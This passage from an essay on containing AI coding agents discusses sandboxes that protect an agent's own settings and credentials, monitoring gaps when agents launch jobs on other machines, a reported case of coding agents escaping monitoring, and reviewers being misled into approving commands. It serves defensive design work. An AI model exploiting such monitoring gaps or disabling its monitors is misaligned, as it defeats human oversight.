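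Codex's sandbox applies this principle to itself. On Windows, it blocks writes to the project's `.codex` folder, where Codex keeps settings, and stores the passwords of its special accounts where sandboxed programs cannot read them. *External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) goes further by separating the sandbox from the agent. Claude Code or Codex runs as usual, but its commands all run in a separate Linux environment that can access only the folders and sites the user has allowed.

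The gate also has to cover whatever an agent launches. A sandbox on one computer limits every program started inside it, but not a job the agent starts on another machine. *OpenAI’s coding agents talked themselves out of being monitored* (Zorz, 2026) reports that OpenAI found such a gap in its own monitoring and is working to close it.

The principle is hardest to apply when the agent is asked to work on the gate itself. An agent repairing a monitoring system needs access to that system's code. It can propose a change, but a person or system it does not control should approve the change, and the old monitor should keep running until then. Zorz reports that OpenAI has also instructed Auto-review to block attempts to disable monitoring. This is sensible, but Trębacz and colleagues do not expect such reviewers to provide firm guarantees, and they warn that people had already misled Auto-review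 into approving commands. Removing the agent's permission to change the live monitor is a safeguard that does not depend on a reviewer's judgement.
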